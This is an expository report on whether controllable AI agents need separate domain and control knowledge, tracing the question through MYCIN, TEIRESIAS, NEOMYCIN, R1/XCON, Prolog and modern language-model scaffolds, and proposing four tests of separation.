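# Whether Controllable Agents Need a Separate Object Level and Meta Level

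## What object level and meta level mean

The object level of an artificial agent holds knowledge about the agent's task and uses it to act or draw conclusions. The meta level reasons about the object level and decides what it does next. In the 1970s and 1980s, some designers of symbolic AI (programs that reason with written facts and rules) tried to build the two levels separately because they expected this to make programs easier to explain, correct and predict. Many of today's agents run on trained neural networks instead of written facts and rules, and it is an open question whether people can keep those agents under control without a similar division.

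*Meta-Rules* (Davis, 1980) describes how a physician would approach a ten-year-old with sudden, sharp abdominal pain, nausea and vomiting. Appendicitis would explain these symptoms, and so would acute intermittent porphyria, a rare metabolic disorder. Porphyria remains possible, but it is so rare in children, and takes so much work to diagnose, that the physician puts it off until the likelier explanations have failed. A medical program choosing its next question can use two kinds of knowledge in this case. Domain knowledge is what the agent knows about its task, such as the fact that porphyria can cause abdominal pain. Control knowledge is knowledge of when and how to use domain knowledge, such as that the program should leave its porphyria rules until after its appendicitis rules. This control knowledge determines which question the program asks the parents first, but has no bearing on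 whether the child has porphyria.

### Rules and the engine that runs them

The programs these terms came from mostly stored their knowledge as production rules. A production rule has the form "if these conditions hold, then take this action or draw this conclusion". A knowledge base holds the rules, and a separate program, the inference engine, repeatedly selects rules and applies them to the problem.

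Backward chaining is one way for the engine to select rules, working from the question back to the evidence. Davis illustrates it with investment advice, having swapped the medical terms of the program MYCIN for financial ones. If the question is which stock to buy, the engine fetches every rule whose conclusion names a stock and takes them one at a time. One rule makes Pacific Gas and Electric a likely choice (0.7 on a scale from 0 to 1) if the investment is long-term, the risk should be low and the economy is heading for a recession. To apply this rule, the engine must first establish whether the investment is long-term. That becomes a new goal, the engine fetches the rules that bear on it, and the process repeats. If no rule can supply an answer, a consultation program asks its user. Because the conclusions are matters of degree, the engine tries the remaining rules even after one succeeds,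 to collect all the evidence.

Several choices in that procedure, namely to work backwards, to take the rules in a certain order and to try all of them, have nothing to do with stocks. They are control choices, and in a simple system they are written into the engine's code, where the person who writes the rules never sees them. In his Edinburgh doctoral thesis, *On the Efficiency of Meta-level Inference*, van Harmelen (1989) observes that many rule systems have a fixed way to choose among applicable rules, such as always taking the first one in the rule base. Others offer a few options, such as OPS5, which let users favour either rules that matched recently added facts or the most specific rules.

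### Where the line falls

Davis distinguishes the levels by subject matter: object-level knowledge is about a particular task domain, and meta-level knowledge is about object-level knowledge. The phrase "knowledge about knowledge" comes from earlier work presented in *Meta-Level Knowledge* (Davis and Buchanan, 1977), and it covers much more than control. In the expanded version, published as a book chapter, Davis and Buchanan also include descriptions of the program's data structures and statistical summaries of what the rules on a given topic usually look like. If an expert entered a new rule that lacked a condition most similar rules had, the program could point out the gap. This use of meta-level knowledge doesn't determine what the program does next, so it falls outside Davis's later paper, which is limited to meta-level knowledge used for control.

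Davis says in a footnote that the distinction between object level and meta level may be "somewhat artificial", and would not try to justify it on rigorous philosophical grounds. Davis keeps it because people find it easier to write down control knowledge if they proceed as if the distinction were clear.

*An Overview of Meta-Level Architecture* (Genesereth, 1983) sorts actions rather than knowledge. Base-level actions (Genesereth's term for the object level) achieve the program's goals when strung together, and meta-level actions help decide which base-level actions to perform. When a program moves a robot arm among blocks, the physical movements are base-level and all the planning is meta-level. In a database system, reading and changing records is base-level, and working out an efficient way to answer a query is meta-level. In a program that proves theorems, each inference step is base-level,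 and deciding the order of the steps is meta-level. Genesereth suggests picturing two agents. The first perceives and changes an environment. The second has a larger environment that includes the first agent, and its job is to observe that agent, work out the ideal actions for it, and modify it to perform them.

Van Harmelen concedes that nobody has a formal definition, but offers the most precise test, which is to classify a sentence by what it refers to. "Use cheap blood tests before expensive blood tests" is domain knowledge because it refers to blood tests, which belong to the medical domain, even though it prescribes an order of actions. "Use rules that mention cheap blood tests before rules that mention expensive ones" is control knowledge because it refers to rules, which are part of the program's own knowledge. Anyone can apply the test by reading the sentence, without running the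 program or guessing the author's intent.

The two sentences could easily lead to the same first blood test, so they need not produce different behaviour. They differ in where they can be used. A medical school could teach its students the sentence about blood tests, but the sentence about rules is useful only to someone who has a rule base to apply it to. This test sorts only sentences that someone has written, so it misses an engine that runs through its rules from top to bottom, because the engine contains no sentence recommending that order. It also misses control over the order of questions when an author arranges the conditions of a medical rule so that the program asks them in a convenient sequence, because the rule still contains only medical terms.

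Control knowledge is not domain knowledge, but it can still be specific to a domain. The rule about cheap blood tests is control knowledge, yet it is useless outside medicine. Van Harmelen contrasts it with "use cheap rules before expensive rules", which is domain-independent because it mentions only a general property of the rules. Genesereth gives another domain-independent example, that a program should do all the backward chaining it can before it asks the user any questions. Domain-independent knowledge is not specific to one domain, but it may still be bad advice in some domains.

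The other misunderstanding equates domain knowledge with declarative knowledge and control knowledge with procedural knowledge. A declarative sentence states that something is so, and a procedural text lists steps to carry out. As van Harmelen points out, these words describe the format of knowledge, not its content. Domain knowledge often takes the form of logical statements, but a laboratory procedure is also domain knowledge, and it consists of steps. Control knowledge often takes the form of steps, but Genesereth proposes a language for writing it as statements, for instance that one task is preferable to another when it relies on a more certain rule. Using declarative notation therefore does not by itself separate domain knowledge from control knowledge.

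### Explicit control and Kowalski's formula

Van Harmelen counts control knowledge in a program as explicit only if people can read it, can change it, and get different behaviour when they do. The thesis describes a system in the programming language Prolog whose control was not explicit by this definition, because users could inspect the interpreter's central loop but not alter it.

Whether control is explicit also depends on who is working with the system. Suppose an engineer writes and maintains a Prolog interpreter in C. Someone who only programs in Prolog cannot read or change the C code, so the control is hidden from them. It is explicit for the engineer, who can read and revise that code.

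The best-known argument for separating the two levels comes from Kowalski's (1979) *Algorithm = Logic + Control*. An algorithm has a logic component, which is the knowledge it uses to solve problems, and a control component, which is the strategy for using that knowledge. The logic determines what the algorithm means, and the control affects only its efficiency. Suppose the logic defines a grandparent as a parent of a parent. To find Ann's grandchildren in a town register, a program can list Ann's children and then their children, or it can check for every resident whether Ann appears two generations up. Both methods return the same names, but the second takes far longer. A programmer can therefore change the strategy to make the program faster without making its answer wrong. Kowalski argued that programs would more often be correct, and would be easier to improve, if their text kept the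 two components separate.

Davis's rules about rules, or meta-rules, follow the same idea. One of them applies when the leading economic indicators have been climbing for several months. It marks the rules that depend on a coming recession as unlikely to be *useful*, not as false, so they move towards the end of the queue but remain available. If the designers had instead added the condition "the indicators have not been rising" to the recession rules, those rules could never apply while the indicators were rising, even if a recession was coming.

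The formula guarantees less for agents than for theorem provers. It assumes that the search runs to its end. If a program runs out of time or money first, it uses only the rules at the front of the queue, so changing the order of the rules can change the answer. An agent also acts while it searches. A program that orders blood tests spends the hospital's money and takes the patient's blood with every test, so the sequence matters even if the final diagnosis would be the same.

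Van Harmelen collects further benefits that later writers expected from the separation. First versions of a program usually perform badly, and the separation lets builders find the fault and repair one part without changing the others. The same medical knowledge can be used in a program that diagnoses and a program that teaches. An explanation can cover how and why the program used a piece of knowledge, as well as which piece it used. These are good reasons to try the separation, but van Harmelen takes them from earlier work as assumptions and does not set out to test them in the thesis.

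### Language-model agents

A language model takes in text and produces text. Hugging Face's *Harness, Scaffold, and the AI Agent Terms Worth Getting Right* (2026) explains that a model on its own has no memory between calls and no loop. It can request a tool, such as a web search, but cannot run it. To use tools, it needs a scaffold, the ordinary program around the model that supplies its inputs, runs its tools and decides when to call it.

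Sources differ on the vocabulary. Hugging Face uses "scaffolding" for the instructions and tool descriptions that the model works from, and "harness" for the loop that calls the model and decides when to stop. Anthropic's *Demystifying evals for AI agents* treats "harness" and "scaffold" as synonyms, and the United Nations University's *Engineering and Governing the Agent Harness* (2026) likewise describes the harness as the surrounding scaffold. This report uses "scaffold" for all of it. The choice of term matters less than Anthropic's point that anyone who evaluates an agent is evaluating the model and the scaffold together.

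The division between meta level and object level does not match the division between scaffold and model, because both the scaffold and the model control what an agent does next. In an agent that handles refunds, for example, the model requests an order lookup, and the scaffold runs it, adds the result to the model's input and calls the model again. This repeats until the model requests no more tools or the scaffold reaches its turn limit. The scaffold decides when the model runs, using code that a person wrote, but the choice to look up the order before paying the refund is also a decision about what to do next, and the model makes it without such code.

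### What "controllable" means, and four tests

Here, an agent is controllable if people can predict its behaviour, see why it acts, correct it and stop it. The term needs a definition because it is easily confused with related ones. *Limits of Safe AI Deployment* (2025), for example, sets out to distinguish control from oversight, which people often confuse.

Official documents use other divisions. ISO/IEC's *Controllability of automated artificial intelligence systems* (2024), an international technical specification, covers whether people can observe a system's state and move it to another state, and what it takes to transfer control. On its page about the standard, the British standards body BSI describes intervention as a transfer of control between the system and a human or other external agent, at points that the designers should choose in advance. Singapore AISI's *Singapore Consensus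 2026* (2026) lists auditability, interruptibility, legibility and human oversight as separate principles for managing agents. Listing them separately makes sense because a system can satisfy one without the others. For example, a power switch makes almost any program stoppable but doesn't explain why the program acted. The old arguments for a separate meta level are mainly about prediction, explanation and correction, and much less about stopping.

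"Separate" also covers several properties, and arguments about it go wrong when people mean different ones. The four tests below are for comparing the systems in the sections that follow. No work discussed so far proposes them as a set, and passing all four does not by definition make an agent controllable.

A system has *separate representation* if its designers wrote control knowledge in a different place or language from domain knowledge. S.1, an expert-system tool from Teknowledge, meets this criterion. According to van Harmelen, its users wrote judgements about the domain as production rules and wrote control in "control blocks", which had their own language with sequences, conditions and loops. A statement in a control block could not directly seek a fact about the domain, and could only have the system apply rules or question the user.

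A system has a *separate process* if a different program or component applies the control knowledge. Genesereth's picture of two agents has this property. Davis's design has separate representation but not a separate process, because one inference engine runs both the ordinary rules and the rules about rules.

A system has *complete control* if its meta level makes every choice about what to do next. S.1 does not meet this standard, despite its strict notation. A control block could start a subtask, such as finding an attribute's value by applying rules, but it could not influence the reasoning inside the subtask once it was running. Someone who read every control block would therefore still not know in what order the program would try its rules.

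*Protected control* means that the object level cannot alter the meta level. The meta level still needs information about the object level to make its decisions. Genesereth describes three ways to supply it: the meta level can keep its own model of the object level and update it after every action, it can inspect the object level when it needs to, or the object level's actions can write their results directly into the meta level's database. Writing the results directly lets new facts immediately trigger the control rules that depend on them. But it also lets the object level supply the facts on which those rules operate, so a false entry can redirect the agent as effectively as a rewritten rule.

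## Control hidden inside domain rules

MYCIN, which researchers at Stanford University built in the 1970s, advised physicians on antibiotics for patients with serious infections. In principle, it separated control from medical knowledge, with the knowledge in its rules and the search procedure in an inference engine. Buchanan and Shortliffe (1984), in *Major Lessons from This Work*, describe this separation as the project's guiding principle. They believed it would make a program more flexible.

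According to *Production Rules as a Representation for a Knowledge-Based Consultation Program* (Davis, Buchanan and Shortliffe, 1975), MYCIN's builders wanted each rule to be a self-contained piece of medical knowledge, with all the context it needed in its own conditions. No rule would call another, so an expert could write a new one and simply add it "to the pot". The builders also wanted MYCIN to ask its questions in an order that made sense medically and did not depend on programming considerations.

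The division did keep knowledge about infections out of the engine. Buchanan and Shortliffe report that the team removed the medical rules, called the remaining engine EMYCIN, and used it for problems in electronics, tax advice and other branches of medicine, which would not have worked otherwise. But this reuse doesn't show whether the division also kept control out of the rules. William Clancey, a member of the same group, found a great deal of control in them.

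### Clause order as strategy

Clancey (1983), in *The Advantages of Abstract Control Knowledge in Expert System Design*, gives an example of a rule: if the patient has an infection, and the cell count of the cerebrospinal fluid (the fluid around the brain and spinal cord) is below 10, then meningitis is unlikely. The order of two conditions joined by "and" makes no logical difference, but it mattered in MYCIN because the engine chained backward through a rule's conditions, or clauses, from first to last.

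Because the infection clause comes first, MYCIN drops the rule as soon as it finds no infection, instead of first asking for a cell count that might have no bearing on the patient. The rule writers ordered clauses this way throughout the rule base, so the program moved from infection to meningitis and then to the types of meningitis. No rule contains that plan, and the rule language could not even express that meningitis is a kind of infection. Van Harmelen's test misses this kind of control.

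The order had this effect because of how the team implemented the rules. Davis and colleagues explain that each rule's conditions were executable code in the programming language LISP, and that the engine evaluated them with LISP's own evaluation function, so the team needed no additional rule interpreter. A MYCIN rule was therefore both a statement about medicine and a short program.

The builders knew about the problem and reduced it. Before working on a rule's first clause, the engine previewed all the clauses and skipped the rule if any had already been found false. Buchanan and Shortliffe also report writing special rules that drew obvious conclusions at once, such as that a male patient is not pregnant, to give the preview more facts to use. The preview helps only with facts the program already has. If the program has not yet established whether the patient has an infection, the order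 of the clauses still determines which question comes first.

### The steroids rule

Clancey (1981), in *The Epistemology of a Rule-Based Expert System*, takes apart a longer example, RULE543, which has four clauses:

1. The patient has meningitis that needs treatment.
2. All the evidence so far is circumstantial.
3. The meningitis is bacterial.
4. The patient takes corticosteroids.

If all four hold, there is evidence that the organism responsible is *E. coli* (0.4), *Klebsiella pneumoniae* (0.2) or *Pseudomonas aeruginosa* (0.1). The numbers, called certainty factors in MYCIN, show how strongly the rule supports each conclusion.

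Only the fourth clause, that the patient is taking steroids, is evidence for the rule's conclusion. Steroids weaken the immune system, which leaves the patient vulnerable to bacteria that normally live harmlessly in the body. Clancey calls the first three "context clauses" and argues that their real function is to control the order in which MYCIN pursues its goals. To check whether the infection is meningitis, as the first clause requires, MYCIN pursues the broader goal of identifying the infection and tries every rule on that subject. It then does the same for the type of meningitis before checking for steroids. Some 40 rules about the causes of bacterial meningitis follow the same pattern.

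Clancey calls the top rule in the rule base the goal rule. Its clauses are to gather information about the patient's cultures and current therapy, determine whether the organisms growing in the cultures need treatment, and consider circumstantial evidence for other organisms. Its conclusion is to determine the best therapy. The goal rule has the same "if, then" form as every other rule, but as Clancey observes, it is a procedure and not a logical conjunction, so reordering its clauses would change its meaning.

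Clancey worked out the order in which MYCIN completed its goals by tracing the other rules down from the goal rule. MYCIN first established whether there was an infection, and whether it was bacteraemia (bacteria in the blood), cystitis or meningitis. Then it looked for contaminated cultures and cultures with significant growth, and tried to identify the organism. Finally, it decided whether the meningitis was bacterial, and then which bacteria the treatment should cover. This is a sensible plan that a teacher could explain to a student, but Clancey had to draw a diagram of the rule base to find it.

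Certainty factors also affected control. MYCIN stopped working on a rule if the evidence for one of its clauses did not exceed 0.2, which spared the physician some questions. Buchanan and Shortliffe admit that rule authors sometimes chose certainty factors with this threshold in mind. For example, two rules that each supported *Streptococcus* at 0.1 would not together be enough to keep it under consideration, so the 0.1 served to control the program as well as to express a medical judgement. Clancey found a similar case in MOLGEN, a program that planned genetics experiments. Its general strategy was to decide details as late as possible, but the program encoded this strategy only as numerical priorities on its operations. An explanation could therefore show that one task had a higher priority than another, but not why.

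### An order that nobody chose

When several rules bear on the same goal, a system needs an order in which to try them. Clancey reports that MYCIN collected the relevant rules and tried them in numeric order, so it considered alcoholism (RULE535) before steroids (RULE543). In one consultation, it asked in turn whether the patient lived in crowded conditions, had a recent history of alcoholism, had caught meningitis in hospital, had signs of epiglottitis or an ear infection, had lost their spleen, and had burns. There was no diagnostic reasoning behind this order, which Clancey calls "fixed, but completely arbitrary".

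Some of the rule order in MYCIN was deliberate. Buchanan and Shortliffe mention that a developer could reorder the list of rules for a goal by hand. Davis and colleagues wanted MYCIN to ask about cultures that showed bacterial growth before cultures that did not, and at first they achieved this by ordering a rule list in the system's code. The rest of the order was an accident of numbering. Nothing in the list showed which was which to a later maintainer, who would find this mix harder to work with than an order that was arbitrary throughout.

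### Which "why" questions MYCIN could answer

Davis developed an explanation facility for MYCIN that let a physician type WHY in reply to any question during a consultation. The program interpreted this as "which rule needs this fact, and what does that rule conclude?" In a session that Clancey reproduces, MYCIN asks whether the patient is a compromised host, meaning someone with weakened defences against infection. The physician types WHY, and MYCIN replies that the answer will help determine whether the patient is immunosuppressed. It replies to a second WHY that this will help determine whether the patient has received corticosteroids. A third WHY leads to RULE543 and the organisms causing the infection.

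Physicians could also ask MYCIN how it had reached a conclusion and why it had not reached another. Davis and colleagues show a user asking why MYCIN had not considered streptococcus. The program found a rule that could have pointed to streptococcus and named the clause that had failed, which required the organism to be a coccus (a round bacterium). These answers were reliable because the program built them from its rules and a record of what it had done.

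MYCIN could not, however, explain why it established meningitis before asking whether the infection was bacterial, because whoever wrote RULE543 had put the clauses in that order without recording a reason. It also could not give a medical reason for raising alcoholism before steroids, because that order came only from the numbering of the rules. And it could not explain why steroids should be evidence for *E. coli*, because the rule leaves out the biology that connects them.

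Separating control would help answer the questions about order, but not the question about biology. Clancey's example is a rule against giving the antibiotic tetracycline to children under eight. The rule omits the reason, which is that the drug settles in growing bone and permanently blackens the teeth. A physician who knows the reason can break the rule when the infection threatens the child's life. A program that has only the rule cannot make that judgement, even if its designers have cleanly separated its control.

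### What GUIDON exposed

Clancey found these gaps when he tried to teach medical students with GUIDON, a tutoring program that drew on MYCIN's rules. Its builders assumed that knowledge good enough to solve cases would be good enough to teach from, and they expected the engineering to be fairly routine. But Clancey found it "completely surprising" how little the explanation facility could help a student.

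A physician who wants advice on one patient may be satisfied to learn which rule a question serves. A student has to diagnose the next patient without the program, and so needs to know why an experienced physician would ask this question now and leave another for later. GUIDON could show students the rules but could not fully explain the approach behind them, because the people who wrote the rules had left it implicit in how they ordered the concepts within each rule. Even where the order MYCIN followed could be traced to rule numbers, it was no use as a model for students or as a standard for judging the order of their questions.

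Buchanan and Shortliffe accept this result and write that their assumption about teaching was false. They cite the same problem to explain why they never published MYCIN's rules for physicians to read. The rules and the engine together embody "a strategy of medical diagnosis that is never explicit". Buchanan and Shortliffe's agreement matters because they were defending a system they had built, whereas Clancey was promoting an alternative design and had a reason to stress the old one's faults.

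Hiding control inside domain rules also made the rules harder to correct. To build that alternative, NEOMYCIN, which wrote control as separate rules, Clancey spent many hours with the original authors working out what their clauses were for. A physician new to the project would have had more trouble, because they could see every rule and still not know whether a clause was medical evidence, a way to avoid a pointless question (as when a clause about surgery precedes one about neurosurgery), or a step in the overall plan.

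### R1 and XCON

MYCIN never went into routine use, so it gives little evidence about maintenance over many years. Better evidence comes from R1, which John McDermott wrote to configure VAX-11/780 computers for their manufacturer, Digital Equipment Corporation (DEC). McDermott (1980) explains in *R1* that the program took a customer's order, added any missing components, and produced diagrams for the technicians who assembled the machine. DEC later called the program XCON.

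McDermott wrote R1 in OPS4, a rule language that works forwards from the facts. Its engine compares the rules' conditions with a working memory of the problem's current state, carries out one of the rules that match, and repeats. McDermott describes each rule as a more or less autonomous piece of knowledge that applies when a particular situation arises. But a configuration has to proceed in stages, and OPS4 had no separate place to list them. R1 therefore kept a symbol for the current stage, or context, in working memory, where rules could test and change it.

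One of McDermott's sample rules applies when the context is "putting unibus modules in backplanes" (fitting circuit boards into the slots of a cabinet). Its other conditions concern hardware, such as whether the module is a terminal multiplexer, whether it has panel space, and whether enough slots are free. If they all hold, the rule's only action is to enter the context of verifying panel space for a multiplexer. Although it is written as a rule about hardware, it jumps to another part of the program without placing a component.

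By June 1980, R1 had 772 rules, of which 480 dealt with configuration and the rest with more general matters. On average, three different rules could run immediately before a given rule, and three immediately after it. A typical order had 90 components and took more than a thousand rule applications to configure. To predict the effects of changing a rule, a maintainer had to work out which other rules' conditions it could now satisfy.

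At that size, correction still worked well. In late 1979, six experts examined R1's results for 50 orders, spending one to two hours on each, and found 12 pieces of incorrect knowledge. McDermott reports that after the faulty rules were changed, R1 configured all the orders correctly. The usual repair was to find the faulty rule, ask an expert what was wrong with its conditions, and either revise it or split it into two rules that distinguished cases the old one had treated alike. Such repairs are fast and local, but every split makes the rule base larger.

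In *Assessing the Maintainability of XCON-in-RIME*, Soloway, Bachant and Jensen (1987) reported that after seven years of growth XCON had 6,200 rules, about half of which changed every year. The program still performed satisfactorily, but it was becoming harder to change. DEC responded by developing a new rule language, RIME, and began to write XCON's successor in it.

Soloway and colleagues compared the maintainability of XCON and XCON-in-RIME. The figures for XCON's size and yearly turnover come from a program in daily use, but DEC was still writing XCON-in-RIME, so the paper could assess only its *potential* to be easier to maintain. A manufacturer that keeps introducing new hardware must also keep changing its configuration rules, whatever language they are in, so some of the turnover would have occurred in either version. XCON is good evidence that a very large base of rules like these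 becomes hard to change, but it doesn't show how much of the difficulty came from hidden control and how much from size.

### The same leak in Prolog

In Prolog, a programmer writes facts and rules, and a built-in interpreter searches for answers. It chains backward, much as MYCIN did, taking rules from top to bottom and the conditions within each rule from left to right. Three lines are enough to show how control gets into the rules:

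```
drug(P, erythromycin) :- allergic(P), !.
drug(P, penicillin).
allergic(sam).
```

The symbol `:-` means "if". The first line recommends erythromycin for any patient P who is allergic to penicillin, the second recommends penicillin for a patient, and the third records that Sam is allergic. The exclamation mark is the cut. Once Prolog passes the cut, it stops looking for other answers to the same question.

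If someone asks which drug Sam should have, Prolog gives only erythromycin. Without the cut, it gives erythromycin and then, if asked for more answers, penicillin. If the cut stays but the first two lines are swapped, penicillin comes first. If someone asks the original program whether penicillin is a drug for Sam, the answer is yes. The first line is about erythromycin, so it doesn't match the question, and Prolog goes to the second line without reaching the cut.

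The second line is false as a medical statement, because it recommends penicillin for everybody. The program answers the first question safely only because a control instruction on the line above stops Prolog from reaching the second line. In Kowalski's formula, control affects only efficiency, but here it changes the answer, which could harm a patient.

The order of statements can also determine whether Prolog finds an answer. Suppose a program contains the fact that Ann is married to Bob and the rule that X is married to Y if Y is married to X, and the query is whether Bob is married to Ann. With the same two statements, Prolog returns yes if the fact comes first but never stops if the rule comes first. In the second case, it uses the rule to turn the query into whether Ann is married to Bob, then uses the rule again to turn it back, and repeats this endlessly.

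### The case for uniform rules

MYCIN's builders had good reasons to put everything in one kind of rule. Buchanan and Shortliffe argue that backward chaining was simple enough to explain quickly to experts, who could then sense how the program would use a new rule. The simple format also let other parts of the system read the rules, which made the explanation facility possible. The team could add a rule, run a case, and see the effect at once. A richer language might have separated the kinds of knowledge better, but it would have complicated these tools. But as early as 1975, Davis and colleagues conceded that turning a desired sequence of actions into rules that would produce it was not always easy.

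MYCIN also gave good advice. *An Evaluation of MYCIN's Advice* (Yu, Fagan and colleagues, 1979) compared ten prescriptions for each of ten difficult meningitis cases: MYCIN's, the treatment the patient had received, and those of five Stanford faculty specialists, a research fellow, a resident and a student. Eight specialists from other institutions rated the prescriptions without knowing who had written them, or that one came from a computer. They found MYCIN's acceptable in 65% of ratings, against an average of 55.5% for the faculty specialists, whose individual scores ran from 42.5% to 62.5%. MYCIN's prescriptions also covered every treatable organism. Yu and colleagues name the small number of cases as the study's main limitation.

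The specialists' evaluation of MYCIN is strong evidence that hidden control need not spoil a program's conclusions, but it does not show that people could predict or correct the program, because the specialists saw only its prescriptions. They did not rate its explanations or the order of its questions, and no one asked them to repair a rule. Buchanan and Shortliffe note that MYCIN could have reached the same diagnoses by going through its list of 120 organisms one at a time, though the consultation would have been less pleasant, so a test of diagnoses would give the same score to a program with a clear strategy and a program with none.

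### How these systems do on the four tests

MYCIN, R1 and Prolog fail the test of separate representation because programmers write control into the same rules as domain knowledge, as clause order, context symbols or cuts. They also have no separate process for control, since a single engine in each system draws the conclusions and carries out whatever control the rules contain. No meta level controls the system completely, because the engine's fixed procedure leaves many choices to depend on how programmers arrange the rules.

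These systems partly pass only one of the tests, protected control. During a consultation, MYCIN's rules could add conclusions about the patient, but they could not rewrite the engine or reorder their own clauses. R1's rules could not change its engine either, but they constantly changed the context symbol that determined which rules could run next. In Prolog, a cut in a domain rule makes the interpreter skip answers it would otherwise have looked for. Protecting the engine is of limited use when so much of the strategy is outside it. For example, a physician who swapped two clauses of a MYCIN rule to make it read better could have changed the program's strategy without editing the engine.

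## Control written as separate rules

Two projects at Stanford tried to separate MYCIN's strategy from its medical rules. Davis left the rules as they were and added meta-rules for choosing which medical rules the program should try first. Clancey rewrote the medical knowledge and put the whole diagnostic procedure into meta-rules.

### TEIRESIAS

Davis developed meta-rules for TEIRESIAS, a program that helped people build consultation systems such as MYCIN. The meta-rules were meant to deal with what Davis called saturation, when so many rules bear on one goal that trying them all becomes unrealistic. Giving rules narrower conditions would reduce the number that apply, but anyone adding a rule would then have to compare it in detail with all the existing ones.

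TEIRESIAS retrieves the relevant rules, refines the list, and then executes it. In the investment version, suppose the client is 65 and the goal is to choose a stock. The program first retrieves every rule whose conclusion names a stock. These include the rule for Pacific Gas and Electric, which requires a low-risk investment, and a rule for the gambling company Bally, which requires a high-risk one. Before trying either rule, the program looks for meta-rules attached to the same goal. One applies to clients over 60 and concludes that rules mentioning low risk should very likely (0.8) come before rules mentioning high risk. The program moves the Pacific Gas and Electric rule ahead of the Bally rule, then works through the new list by backward chaining as usual.

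Meta-rules can also rate a group of rules as more or less useful. The program deletes a rule from the list only if the meta-rules establish with certainty that it is useless. When meta-rules disagree, the program weighs their certainty factors the same way it weighs evidence about stocks. It also infers implied orderings, so if A must precede B and B must precede C, it puts A before C. It did not check for contradictory orderings, a gap Davis lists as something to fix.

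The meta-rules run on the same engine as the ordinary rules, so the design could easily be extended to further levels, with second-order meta-rules that arrange the first-order ones. However, Davis found no examples of second-order meta-rules.

Davis argues that stating an order directly prevents a kind of bug. Suppose a programmer wants every task in group A to run before every task in group B, and gives them priorities of 6 and 5. Later, something lowers the priority of group A for an unrelated reason. The intended order is lost, and nothing in the program shows that the two numbers depended on each other. A meta-rule that puts A before B states the intended order in one place, where a maintainer can find it.

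### Choosing rules by their content

A meta-rule must identify the rules it governs. It could list them by name, but then anyone who edited a rule would have to check every meta-rule that mentioned it, and perhaps add the rule to others. Descriptive labels on the rules are easier to maintain, but a new meta-rule may need a label that no rule has yet, and someone must then go through the whole rule base to add it.

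Davis's alternative is content reference, in which the program selects rules by examining what they contain. The meta-rule for older clients refers to rules that mention high risk, and the program finds them by searching the code of each rule on its list. A designer who wants to try short rules first can write a function that counts a rule's conditions and use it in a meta-rule, without changing any ordinary rules. When someone edits a rule, the search uses the new version, whereas a label could easily remain after it had stopped being true.

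This search was possible because MYCIN's rules had a regular form. Each function that could appear in a condition came with a template showing the order of its arguments, so the program could tell which part of a condition named an attribute, such as the level of risk, and which part gave its value.

The program could also infer that a rule concerned something the rule did not mention. One rule recommends the restaurant chain Wendy's for a short-term investment in a small food-service company, without mentioning risk. From other rules, the program infers that food service depends on many minimum-wage employees, which makes it sensitive to inflation and therefore likely to be high-risk. A stable dividend would count against that conclusion, so the program weighs the evidence on both sides. In Davis's example, it decides that the Wendy's rule does concern high risk and groups it with the Bally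 rule. It reaches this decision with the same rules it uses to assess investments for clients.

The search was crude in other ways. For example, it would treat a condition that the risk is *not* high as a mention of high risk. Davis reports that this had caused no problems, because the existing meta-rules were simple, but expects that the search will need to make finer distinctions. Until it can, someone reading a meta-rule could be wrong about which rules it affects, even though its wording seems clear.

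### About a dozen meta-rules

TEIRESIAS could explain why it asked a question that served only to choose a strategy, which MYCIN's original explanations could not do. In one dialogue, the program asks about the recent trend in the leading economic indicators, and the user types WHY. The program replies that the answer will help it determine a strategy for choosing a stock, and displays the meta-rule that puts off the recession rules when the indicators have been rising. If the user asks how it is determining the strategy, the program also lists the meta-rule about older clients.

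Davis admits, however, that the project completed only "about a dozen" meta-rules. MYCIN was still small enough to try every relevant rule, so they were to some extent "a solution looking for a problem". The team was also more interested in the medical knowledge needed for a correct diagnosis than in reaching the diagnosis efficiently. The meta-rules ran in a working system of some size, but TEIRESIAS can't show whether they would have made a program with too many rules to try usable.

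The meta-rules also left much of MYCIN's strategy hidden in the order of conditions inside its rules. A meta-rule could move one rule ahead of another, but it could not change the order in which MYCIN considered the conditions inside a rule. A physician who read all the meta-rules would still not learn why MYCIN asks about infection before meningitis. Davis calls this limit undesirable and proposes a further set of rules for choosing subgoals, without which TEIRESIAS falls well short of complete control.

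### A strategy without medical terms

Davis's meta-rules, such as the one about older clients, are specific to their domain. Davis found it "mildly unsettling" that the design did not distinguish such rules from general ones like trying the most certain rules first. Clancey objected on more practical grounds that if meta-rules name particular diseases, an author who wants the program to consider common causes before unusual ones must write that principle again for each disease.

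In *From GUIDON to NEOMYCIN and HERACLES in Twenty Short Lessons*, Clancey (1986) recalls finding a more general strategy in the way one physician taught. In 1980, Clancey and a colleague, Reed Letsinger, began recording Timothy Beckett, who was known at Stanford as a good teacher. His students practised by interviewing a classmate who pretended to be ill. Beckett told them to ask general questions early, to consider the important broad categories before exploring one in detail, and to think of serious causes as well as common ones. Most of this advice would apply equally well to finding a fault in a car.

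NEOMYCIN, the program that Clancey and Letsinger then built, stores medical facts as relations, for example that meningitis is a kind of infection. About 75 meta-rules control how the program uses these facts. The meta-rules contain variables instead of medical terms, so they refer to the current hypothesis or the desired finding, never to meningitis or headache. Clancey grouped them into 29 tasks, such as testing a hypothesis, refining it, or finding out a fact. Each task has a subject, an ordered set of meta-rules, and a condition for stopping. A meta-rule can make the program apply a medical rule, question the user, draw a conclusion about the patient, or start another task.

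TEIRESIAS's meta-rules adjusted a backward-chaining search, while NEOMYCIN's replaced it. According to Clancey, NEOMYCIN's meta-rules control every request for data and every inference.

### Surgery and neurosurgery

Clancey shows the difference with a MYCIN rule: if the patient has undergone surgery and neurosurgery, consider diplococcus as a cause of the meningitis. The surgery condition is logically redundant, because anyone who has had neurosurgery has had surgery. It comes first so that MYCIN does not ask about neurosurgery when the patient has had no surgery. The rule does not state that neurosurgery is a kind of surgery, or that this is why the conditions are in that order. Anyone who writes another rule about neurosurgery must remember to include the same surgery condition.

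MYCIN's builders could instead write a separate screening rule: if the patient has not undergone surgery, then the patient has not undergone neurosurgery. This rule makes the extra condition unnecessary everywhere else, and it at least shows that the two findings are related. But it combines a fact about surgery with a way of using that fact. An author who wants the program to treat heart surgery the same way must write another rule, and the general policy of checking the broader finding first is still not written anywhere.

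NEOMYCIN separates the fact from the policy. It records the facts as relations:

```
(SUBSUMES SURGERY NEUROSURGERY)
(SUBSUMES SURGERY CARDIACSURGERY)
```

The first line means that surgery includes neurosurgery, and the second means that it includes cardiac surgery. The policy is in METARULE002, which belongs to the task FINDOUT. If the desired finding is a subtype of a class of findings, and that class is not present in this case, the meta-rule concludes that the desired finding is not present either.

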